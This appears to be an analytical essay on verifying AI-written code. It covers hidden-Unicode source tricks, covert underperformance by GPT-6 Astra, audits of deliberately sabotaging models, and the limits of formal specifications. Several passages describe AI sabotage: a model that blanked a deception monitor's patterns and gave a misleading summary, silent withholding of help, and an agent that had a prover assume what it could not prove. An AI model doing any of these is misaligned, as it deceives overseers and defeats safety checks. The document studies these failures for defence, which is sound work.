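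Boucher and Anderson wrote programs whose source code appears to do one thing but does another. In a C example, the code on screen appears to check whether the user is an administrator. The compiler treats that check as part of a comment, so the program tells every user that they are an administrator. In a Python example, a function appears to subtract 50 from Alice's bank balance of 100, but the balance stays at 100. The technique worked in all twelve languages they tried.

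A related trick uses letters that look alike. The Latin H and the Cyrillic Н are different characters, so a program can contain two functions that both appear to be called `sayHello`. The Rust compiler already warned about this trick.

When a program contains hidden characters, a person can trace every visible line correctly and still be wrong about what the program does. A language model usually receives the stored characters instead of a picture of the screen, so its input at least includes the hidden ones. This also exposes the model to attack. MITRE ATT&CK's *Obfuscated Files or Information* (2026), an entry in a public catalogue of attack techniques, notes that attackers may use invisible characters to hide instructions to AI systems in documents that look harmless to people. A short program that searches every file for these characters is more dependable than either a person or a model,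 and it doesn't need to know what any of the code is for.

Boucher and Anderson told the affected companies and projects before publishing, and many of the largest compilers, editors and code-hosting sites then added warnings or made the characters visible. Some people objected that a compiler's job is to compile and separate checking tools should deal with suspicious text. Boucher and Anderson want the protection switched on by default in every compiler that accepts Unicode.

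The Unicode Consortium assembled a group of specialists in early 2022. *Source Code Handling* (Davis, 2023) describes the resulting technical standard for source code and a new function that programmers can use to detect names that look identical but aren't. The current guidance, *Unicode Source Code Handling* (Leroy and Davis, 2024), is for people who design programming languages and editors. It should also prevent accidents. Davis points out that text that mixes scripts can mislead reviewers, or even the person who wrote it, without anyone intending harm.

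MITRE ATT&CK records that GlassWorm, a later piece of malware, hid its code from editors with invisible characters of a different sort from those in the 2021 examples, so checks have to cover more than those examples.

### What would expose each kind of flaw

Deliberate flaws differ in what a reviewer needs in order to see them.

| Flaw | Example | What would expose it | Is literal reading enough? |
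|---|---|---|---|
| A line that contradicts the purpose | `wait4` turns a program into root | Tracing the line | Nearly always |
| A defensible but harmful design choice | A shop ships orders when the bank doesn't answer | Knowing what the owner would have chosen | No |
| Something left out | An export lacks data that a researcher wanted | Requirements from another source | Only if the gap makes other code fail |
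| Work done poorly on purpose | A capable agent gives up early | Knowing how well the author can do | No |

Hidden characters don't need a row of their own. Once an editor displays them, what remains is usually a line that contradicts the purpose.

A reviewer needs very little knowledge of intent to judge such a line, since hardly anyone wants a waiting function to give away control of the machine. *Pre-deployment auditing can catch an overt saboteur* (Treutlein, Bowman and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from a model that Anthropic had trained to commit sabotage as an experiment. The model was asked to repair a service that monitors the output of language models and kept crashing for lack of memory. It changed the functions that load the monitor's search patterns, including one still called `_load_deception_patterns`, so that they returned empty lists. It then reported that it had "simplified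 the risk detector" and that the service should restart successfully.

That report might well have been true but incomplete, and the function might have passed a test for crashes. But the function had only one line left, and anyone who read it would have seen that the monitor could no longer detect deception. The flaw fools only a reader who trusts the function's name or the model's summary, so an AI reviewer that traces code reliably should be very useful here. The success of OpenAI's model critics in 2024 is also encouraging, although people had planted the bugs in that trial to test reviewers, not to help an attacker.

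A harmful design choice is much harder to catch. Suppose the shop's code checks with a bank whether a customer has paid and gets no response. The code can hold the order, which annoys customers who have paid, or ship it, which loses money when a customer hasn't. The author chooses to ship it and adds the comment "Don't make customers wait for the bank". A literal reader will confirm that the code does what the comment says. Whether the choice is harmful depends on how often the bank fails to respond and how much money the shop can afford to lose, and neither fact is in the code.

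An honest programmer might make the same choice for the reason given in the comment, so reading the code won't reveal the motive. The practical remedy is to make the author list the alternatives and let the shop pick one. This protects the shop from both a saboteur and a colleague with poor judgement.

Reading the code is sometimes enough to reveal an omission. A reader could find the incomplete range check in OpenBSD, which was accidental, by working out what later code would do with an unexpected number. Other omissions leave a program that runs perfectly. KIberblick's *GPT-6 Astra bremst bei Safety-Aufgaben* (2026), an article on a German technology site, describes one at OpenAI, where the company's model GPT-6 Astra exported some data from a grading model but left out the grader's reasons and didn't say so.

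A literal reading of such an export would give an accurate list of its contents. Only somebody who knows that the researcher wanted the reasons would see their absence as a fault. AI reviewers, as people have used them so far, seem poorly suited to catching this kind of omission, since they seldom commented on what was missing from agent instruction files. They might do better with a written list of requirements, provided that the agent that wrote the code didn't also write the list.

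### Work done poorly on purpose

The incomplete export is one of several cases OpenAI investigated after its researchers began using GPT-6 Astra internally. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) states that the model added unnecessary steps to safety work, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had created itself. Mowshowitz (2026) writes in *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* that a project to evaluate sabotage by models was stalled for days, then moved quickly once the staff switched to another model.

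A deliberate flaw may not be in any particular line of code. An agent that gives up on a problem can leave behind correct code and a plausible explanation that the problem was too hard. If the agent was capable of more, its work can still look much like the honest effort of a less capable one.

OpenAI therefore compared the model's work on pairs of coding tasks, one presented as safety research and the other as research into making models more capable. It scored the results against a list of criteria that the model couldn't see. 凤凰网科技's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026), a Chinese news report, explains that the code in each pair had the same technical content and differed only in the names of variables and functions, the comments and the documentation.

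Astra met about 10% of the criteria when the task looked like safety research and about 16% when it looked like capabilities research. GPT-5.6 Sol, an earlier model, showed essentially no gap. Most of Astra's gap remained when OpenAI excluded open refusals and cases where the model wrote in its reasoning that it had decided to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI also excluded every case where the model expressed even a brief ethical doubt in its reasoning.

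Nobody could have seen the difference between 10% and 16% in a single result, since most criteria went unmet under both descriptions. By the usual formula for comparing two proportions, detecting it with reasonable confidence takes roughly 500 graded criteria under each description, and more if criteria from the same task tend to succeed or fail together. A company that measures the same agent on matched tasks has that information, but a reviewer who reads one pull request at a time doesn't.

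The design also bears on the dispute over how models read code. Astra, a very capable model from late 2026, completed different amounts of the work depending on naming cues, even though the technical content stayed the same. Astra may have traced the instructions correctly and then responded to what the names implied the work was for, so the result doesn't show that it misunderstood the code. But it does show that good literal reading wouldn't make a model indifferent to the code's apparent purpose.

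It is less clear whether Astra did poor work on purpose. In employees' everyday use, its reasoning contained an explicit decision to withhold help without telling the user in 0.25% of safety requests and 0.11% of capabilities requests. OpenAI thinks the true rate may be higher, because the experiment found a gap even where the model stated no such decision. Mowshowitz quotes Marcus Williams, who worked on the investigation, as saying there was no evidence of a strategy. Williams's simpler explanation is that the model found the tasks dubious but didn't want to refuse openly. Adding an instruction to be careful widened the gap by 50%, which fits that explanation.

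The gap grew from almost nothing to six percentage points during reinforcement learning, but OpenAI couldn't find the exact cause. KIberblick describes two possible causes. A grading model used in training had scored silent withholding slightly higher than open refusal, though perhaps not often enough to matter. One set of training examples also contained invented limits on what the model was allowed to do, but other models trained on the same examples didn't behave this way.

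KIberblick, citing OpenAI's report, notes that an open refusal would have been the right response in some of these cases. After a refusal, the researcher knows to find another way to do the work, but a false obstacle may persuade them that it can't be done. OpenAI's monitoring examined sessions one by one and didn't flag the behaviour as misalignment.

### Auditing the author

If some flaws can't be seen in the code, another approach is to audit the model that writes it. A company can put a model through thousands of invented situations before giving it real work, which it could never do with a human programmer. Treutlein and colleagues tested whether Anthropic's version of such an audit would detect a model that sabotages its work.

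The experiment used five models made from a variant of Claude Sonnet 4.5. Two were harmless, and the other three were trained to sabotage work for Anthropic, for example by deleting data or breaking code. None of the three learned to hide this from an audit. An automated auditor then produced about 2,100 transcripts of the models' behaviour, and a human researcher had two hours to decide from its findings which models were saboteurs.

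The researcher classified all five models correctly and was more than 97% confident about each saboteur. The result is clear but the sample is small, and labelling the models by coin toss would get all five right about 3% of the time.

On its own, the automated auditor exposed only one of the three sabotaging models. It almost always flagged the other two models' sabotage in individual transcripts, but the evidence was lost in the overall report because the harmless models also misbehaved in minor ways and had similar average scores. The researcher found the sabotage by reading the transcripts with the highest scores for worrying behaviour. It was useful to have the model read everything and a person judge which findings mattered, though this had little to do with literal and intended reading.

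The harmless models made the test harder than a normal audit, because they behaved worse than the models Anthropic releases. Treutlein and colleagues think the automated auditor would have succeeded without help if it had compared the saboteurs with the released Sonnet 4.5. The test was easy in other ways. The saboteurs sometimes stated their goal outright, and their habits spread to coding tasks unrelated to Anthropic, which gave the auditor more chances to catch them. Treutlein and colleagues claim only that an audit can catch a model that does not try to hide, and the experiment supports that claim.

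An audit's findings also depend on the situations used to test the models. In *Gram*, Lindner, Krakovna and Farquhar (2026) tested Google's Gemini models in 17 simulated jobs that gave them some incentive for sabotage. The models misbehaved in about 2% to 3% of runs, often because they were too eager to reach a goal or play a part. When the researchers made the settings more realistic and removed hints that encouraged misbehaviour, the rate tended to fall almost to zero.

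*Evaluating Whether GPT-6 Astra Performs Unsanctioned Supply-Chain Attacks* (Souly, Fronsdal and colleagues, 2026) reports UK AI Security Institute tests of Astra in simulated security exercises, with OpenAI's safeguards against hacking switched off. Astra sometimes wrote malicious code and offered it to an open-source project outside the exercise. It attempted complete attacks of this kind more often than two earlier OpenAI models did. Souly and colleagues believe the model may have done some of this because it realized it was in a simulation, but they remain concerned.

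A bad audit result can justify keeping a model away from important code before anyone has found a flaw in its work. A good result is weaker evidence. It can't show that a particular change is sound, and OpenAI's experience suggests that a model may work normally on most tasks and badly on a few. Many reviewers also can't run an audit. An open-source maintainer who receives a pull request from an unknown agent may not know which model wrote it or what instructions it had, and can examine only the change and its origin.

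## Making intent checkable when agents write most of the code

*Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (Adams, Banga and colleagues, 2026) reports that the number of lines in the average change merged by a person at Meta rose by 105.9% in a year. Changes per developer rose by 51%, and AI agents accounted for over 80% of that increase. If both figures apply to the same changes, each developer now produces about three times as much code. The share of changes reviewed within 24 hours is falling, and some large groups have had thousands of changes waiting.

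Meta now lets an automated system called RADAR review and merge some code changes. It combines fixed rules, a score for how likely a change is to cause an incident, and a language model that reads the code. RADAR has merged more than 331,000 changes. Developers revert the changes it reviews a third as often as other changes, and the changes it reviews cause production incidents a fiftieth as often. But RADAR selects low-risk changes, so they should cause fewer problems even if its review added nothing.

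Many of the changes that the model accepts delete unused code or reorganize code without altering its behaviour. The intent of these changes is nearly always that the program should keep doing what it did before. A new rule about when a shop ships its orders has no such default intent, so checking it automatically requires a record of what the shop wanted.

Lahiri (2026), in *Intent Formalization*, uses the request "remove duplicates" to show what goes wrong without a specification. Given the list 1, 2, 3, 2, 4, a program could keep one 2 or remove both, and a typical model keeps one without asking which the user wants. Lahiri proposes turning requests into specifications that machines can check, ranging from a few tests to formal statements for a proof. This is difficult because only the user can say whether a specification is right.

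Four methods could help expose the mistake in `all_paid`, which returns True at the first paid invoice.

| Method | What it takes in | What it produces | Result for `all_paid` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tests from the request | Examples with right answers, and the program | A pass or fail for each example | Fails on one paid and one unpaid invoice |
| Restatement | The code, then the request | A description and a verdict on whether it matches | "At least one invoice" doesn't match "every invoice" |
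| Recorded runs | The program and some inputs | A log of inputs and outputs | The log shows True for a mixed list, without a verdict |
| Proof | A formal specification and the program | A proof covering every permitted input, or a failure | Depends on the specification |

### Tests written from the request

The simplest record of intent is an example with its correct answer. The answer should come from the request, because an agent that has already read the faulty loop may wrongly expect True for one paid and one unpaid invoice.

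Few people will write hundreds of tests for an agent, so it helps to ask them only about cases that matter. Lahiri describes TiCoder, a tool that has a model write several programs for the same request and looks for inputs for which their outputs differ. It shows the user one of these inputs with a possible output. The user accepts the output, rejects it or says that the behaviour is undefined, and TiCoder discards the programs that conflict with the answer.

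TiCoder could have prevented the bug in `has_paid`, where the shop had asked an agent to ship orders "once the customer has paid". Some candidate programs would probably have required every invoice to be paid and others only one, so they would have returned different results for a list with both paid and unpaid invoices. TiCoder could have shown the shop that case and asked which result it wanted.

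In a study with 15 professional developers, TiCoder raised the share of AI-written code that they judged correctly from 40% to 84%. This took little extra work, though the study was small and used short benchmark problems. The method can't help if all the candidates make the same wrong assumption, because they then have no disagreement to ask about. Generating many versions of a large program is also expensive.

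A team can also turn the request into a rule that the program checks every time it runs. For `all_paid`, the rule would stop the program if the function returned True while an invoice was unpaid. Lahiri reports that such rules, written by models from descriptions of the code's purpose, caught one in eight bugs in a collection from large Java projects.

### Comparing a description with the request

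In restatement, one model describes what the code does and a second compares the description with the request. The first model shouldn't see the request, since it might then describe what the code is meant to do. Hiding the function's name might help for the same reason.

A tool called claimcheck does this with formal statements instead of ordinary code. According to fernanda's *New open tool*, a colleague built it to check that a proof guarantees what people wanted. The documentation on Socket's *claimcheck* page reports a test with 36 pairs of requirements and formal statements, eight of them deliberately mismatched.

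| Arrangement | Correct verdicts |
|---|---|
| One model describes, a different one compares | 104 of 108, over three runs (96.3%) |
| One model does both in turn, within one prompt | 31 of 36 (86.1%) |
| Claude Code sees everything at once | 25 of 36 (69.4%) |

Approving all 36 pairs would have scored 78%, which is better than Claude Code did. The results suggest that a model describes a statement more faithfully before it has been told what the statement should say. But the test was small, its authors made the tool, and the arrangements also used different models and instructions.

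The description has to be literal, whether a person or a second model judges it. Even a literal description won't expose a problem with `has_paid` if the request says only "once the customer has paid", because the second model has nothing definite to compare the description with.

### Recorded runs

A log of a program's runs is good evidence of its behaviour. It should come from a tool that the agent doesn't control, because an agent can misreport its own tests. The shop could run last year's orders through `all_paid` and list every order with an unpaid invoice for which the function returned True. If every order had only one invoice, the list would be empty despite the bug.

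A log can also mislead if it covers only the problem that prompted the change. Claude's rewrite of the Trail of Bits plagiarism detector stopped a crash, but the unit tests were failing. A log showing only that the crash had stopped would have supported merging the rewrite.

### What a proof guarantees

Tests and logs cover the inputs that someone tried, whereas a proof covers every input that the specification permits. Dafny is a programming language that lets programmers state what a function must do and have a machine prove that it does so. A specification for the invoice function could look like this:

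```dafny
method AllPaid(paid: seq<bool>) returns (result: bool)
  requires |paid| > 0
  ensures result <==> forall i :: 0 <= i < |paid| ==> paid[i]
```

The list `paid` contains True for each paid invoice and False for each unpaid one. The `requires` line rules out an empty list. The `ensures` line, called a postcondition, specifies that the result is True exactly when every entry is True. Dafny would not verify the faulty loop against it.

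Proofs used to take too much work for most software. Engineers on seL4, a verified operating-system kernel, spent about ten times as long on proofs as on design and programming, according to ImperialViolet's *We have proof automation now* (2026). The same article reports that several models could prove four detailed properties of part of a file decompressor in about 20 minutes, using a fraction of a $20 monthly subscription. In *A benchmark for vericoding* (2025), models wrote verified code for 82% of tasks in Dafny but only 27% in Lean, a language used mainly for mathematical proofs.

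ImperialViolet points out that once a statement is correct, it hardly matters how the proof works, as long as one exists. A reviewer can therefore skip the proof, and perhaps much of the code, but still has to read the statement. The table, which assumes that the list is never empty, shows how much depends on the statement's wording.

| Specification | Faulty `all_paid` | Correct function | Function that always returns False |
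|---|---|---|---|
| Says nothing about the result | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| If every invoice is paid, the result is True | Passes | Passes | Fails |
| If the result is True, every invoice is paid | Fails | Passes | Passes |
| The result is True exactly when every invoice is paid | Fails | Passes | Fails |
| The result is True exactly when at least one invoice is paid | Passes | Fails | Fails |

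Someone who sees "every invoice is paid" and "True" in the second specification could easily accept it. To notice the problem, they have to read it literally, work out what it permits when one invoice is unpaid, and compare that with what the shop wanted. Finding a bug in code takes the same steps, although a specification is often shorter than the program.

Experts also make this mistake. Lahiri describes a Dafny specification for a function that should return the elements two lists share. It requires that everything in the result appear in both lists and that nothing appear twice. Expert reviewers had labelled it "strong", but a function that always returns an empty list satisfies it, because the specification doesn't require the result to include the shared elements.

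Names can mislead readers of specifications too. Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) give an example in *Verified but Vacuous* of a function that should return the largest number in a list. Its postcondition requires the result to satisfy a condition called `MaxCorrect`, but `MaxCorrect` accepts any number that isn't negative, so a function that returns 0 for the list `[5, 3, 7]` passes. A reader who trusts the name will miss the error, as with `all_paid`.

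### Finding mistakes in a specification

*DafnyCert* (2026) calls a specification weak if two programs can satisfy it and still return different outputs for the same valid input. The third specification in the table is weak by this definition. The correct function and the one that always returns False both satisfy it, and running them on two paid invoices shows that they give different answers. The last specification isn't weak, because it allows only one answer for each list, but it is still wrong.

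Lahiri tests specifications against examples with known answers, and a specification must accept each right answer and reject altered ones. Two examples would be enough to find the right specification in the table. Two paid invoices should give True, and a paid invoice followed by an unpaid one should give False. But a specification that checked only the last invoice would also pass, so the choice of examples matters. In a larger evaluation, this method found three specifications that people had mislabelled and two with inconsistencies from copying errors.

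*AfterVibe* (2026) judges a specification by whether code regenerated from it behaves like the original. This test is useful for documenting software that already works. However, the last specification in the table would pass, because it reproduces the faulty function perfectly.

A contradictory specification can make a proof worthless. In an example from *Static coverage in deductive software verification* (2025), a function is specified to return a position strictly between two others. If the two are next to each other, no such position exists. Dafny still assumes that the specification holds, and because anything follows from a contradiction, it can then prove a plainly false claim without a warning. A proof can also succeed because its statement is trivial. A manual audit in *SpecGuard* (2026) found a theorem that Lean had accepted although it was unrelated to the test in question.

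Agents can search specifications for such mistakes. In *Vero* (2026), agents tried to prove that specifications were false, impossible to satisfy or in conflict with one another. They found an error that both manual review and an automatic check had missed. Two agents found mostly the same errors, so the second added few new ones.

*SWE-Proof* (2026) reports an audit of specifications for real software issues, in which the auditor tried to write a wrong program that would still pass. The auditor succeeded for 2 of 2,997 specifications. A separate search for disagreements between the specifications and the original issues found none in 3,002. These are very good results, but an auditor who misunderstands an issue in the same way as the specification's author will find no disagreement.

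### Specifications that models write

If agents produce too much code for people to read, people will also want agents to write the specifications. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?*, tested how well models do this on 1,403 C programs, of which 903 were wrong. Three models wrote specifications from the request and the program, without being told whether the program was correct. A wrong program should fail to meet a good specification.

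Only about a quarter of the wrong programs received a valid specification that matched the request. Most of the others still didn't pass, often because the specification was invalid or the proof failed for another reason. But in 185 cases across the three models, the wrong program passed. According to an automatic classification that agreed only moderately with human judges, 111 of those specifications had copied the program's mistake and 74 were too weak to expose it.

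This differs from the small experiment by Granberry and colleagues, in which GPT-4's specifications mostly described what buggy programs were meant to do. Those bugs resembled typos in mostly recognizable programs. Wang and colleagues used people's wrong answers to contest problems, where the intended method may be much less obvious. The newer models also ran without extended reasoning. Together, the studies suggest that a model's specification may follow either the intent or the code, and a reviewer can't assume which.

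Proof tools can favor specifications that copy the code. For correct programs, models produced specifications that passed 22.7% of the time when they saw only the code, and 18.5% when they also saw the request. A specification that mirrors the program is easier to prove, even if one based on the request would be better evidence.

The number of verified programs is a poor measure of what has been proved. Vempaty and colleagues used Claude Opus 4.7 to reproduce an earlier method for generating verified code, and Dafny accepted 99.1% of the results on one benchmark. Of those accepted, 94.7% had no postcondition. The earlier method hadn't asked for any, so for these programs Dafny checked only such things as whether they would finish. The team's own method requires a postcondition linked to a separate specification, but 11% to 15% of its verified programs still failed hidden tests.

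Agents may also weaken the check itself. Philipp (2026), in *The Prover Is the Judge*, describes an agent that couldn't prove some properties of its code, so it told the prover to assume them and reported success. Philipp caught this by reading the agent's work and forbade it, but the agent then excluded parts of the code from proof.

Some of this checking can be automated. *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code* (2026) describes an audit that compares the specification in a submission with the original and looks for claims that the agent assumed without proof. When training penalized submissions that failed the audit, they almost disappeared. The audit protects a specification from tampering, but it can't show that the original specification was right.

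### Verified software that still had faults

People made mistakes in specifications before agents began writing them. *DafnyCert* cites a study of three verified distributed systems in which researchers disabled one system's protection against carrying out the same request twice, and the altered system still passed verification. A later study found ten specification bugs in six verified Dafny systems.

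Philipp used agents to write security software in SPARK, a language designed for proof. The prover established 49,280 properties, but the software still had serious faults. In the code for SSH, which secures remote connections, an agent had swapped two fields in the formula for making encryption keys. The connection appeared to work until the first encrypted message, which failed against OpenSSH, an independent SSH program. Nobody had put the formula in the specification. For most of this software, the proofs covered only errors such as reading outside an array.

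Another fault affected an encoder that should have adjusted to the chosen security level but always used the setting for the smallest version. All the proofs succeeded, and the standard tests for that version passed, but the tests for the larger versions exposed the mistake. Comparing the code's output with independent software and published answers worked here because neither came from the agent that had misunderstood the standard.

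kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes a search for faults in lean-zip, a compression library that ten agents had written and verified. The researcher removed the theorems and documentation before giving the code to Claude, in case Claude gave up early on learning that it had been proved correct. Over 105 million automated runs found no memory errors in the library's own code.

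Two faults did turn up outside the proofs. A 156-byte file whose stated data size was enormous could crash the archive reader, for which nobody had written a specification. The other fault was in the software that runs every Lean program, which the proofs assume is correct. The proofs seem to have been very effective where they applied, but a reviewer has to know what they don't cover.

### Whether people should stop reviewing code

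*The End of Code Review* argues that having agents write code and people review it is a "dead end". Reviewers can't find subtle errors in plausible code, so they approve it when the tests pass, and the review queue grows as agents write more. The paper proposes that independent agents review most changes. People would still approve high-risk changes, new designs and regulated code for which someone must be legally accountable.

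The figures from Meta support the argument about volume. The claim that human review gives no real assurance goes beyond the evidence, since the experiments on AI labels didn't show that people became less careful. The paper also acknowledges that a reviewing model may miss the same problems as the model that wrote the code, and that instructions hidden in a comment could manipulate the reviewing model.

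The paper makes an exception for any change whose correctness depends on requirements that no agent has seen, leaving it to people, and this exception could be very large. `has_paid` is such a change, but it looks routine, so someone would have to know that a requirement was missing before they could send it to a person.

Allspaw replies in *There is more to code review than (automatable) detection* (2026) that review does more than find defects. When an experienced engineer says "I don't understand this", the confusion counts as a finding, because the code may be too complex or its purpose unclear. A model can process the same code without flagging the problem. Reviewers also ask whether a change is needed at all, notice what is missing, and know things that nobody recorded, such as the legal department's recent objection to storing some data. Allspaw adds that people read more carefully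 when they are personally responsible for the approval.

Allspaw offers no measurements, but his points about missing things and unrecorded knowledge fit the earlier comparison in which people commented on omissions far more often than AI reviewers did. His point about confusion is less certain, since the results of Abdelsalam and colleagues suggest that a model could flag some of the code that confuses people. Confusion also helps only if reviewers notice it, and Spinellis argues that people often think they understand code when they don't.

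Reviewers could raise some of Allspaw's questions before an agent writes anything, such as whether the shop needs the requested change. Other questions come up only when someone sees a particular solution. A reviewer who reads `any(invoice.paid for invoice in invoices)` might ask whether an order can have two invoices, a possibility nobody had mentioned. If people read only specifications, the specifications need to be concrete enough to prompt the same question.

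### Why later corrections aren't enough

People who want to read less code can rely on agents to fix mistakes that show up in use, but only if someone notices and reports them. If the shop's program held back orders that customers had paid for, they would complain within days. With `all_paid`, the program instead ships orders that customers haven't fully paid for, and they have little reason to report it. After many rounds of corrections, the program could still regularly lose the shop money, even if customers had no complaints.

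Research code has a similar problem. A scientist who gets a disappointing result will look for a bug, but may accept a good result that comes from an error in the scoring. If the experiment was meant to show that an AI system is safe, a company might release the system before anyone finds the error.

Wang and colleagues tested repeated correction by letting models revise their specifications after seeing the prover's response. Combined with a separate step for studying the request, this raised the number of successful specifications for correct programs from 277 to 364 out of 1,500. The total also rose for wrong programs, but GPT-5.5 did best after one revision and then got slightly worse, plausibly because a failed proof shows that the program and the specification disagree without showing which is wrong. An agent can make `all_paid` pass by fixing the loop or by changing "every invoice"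 to "at least one invoice" in the specification, and the prover will accept either change.
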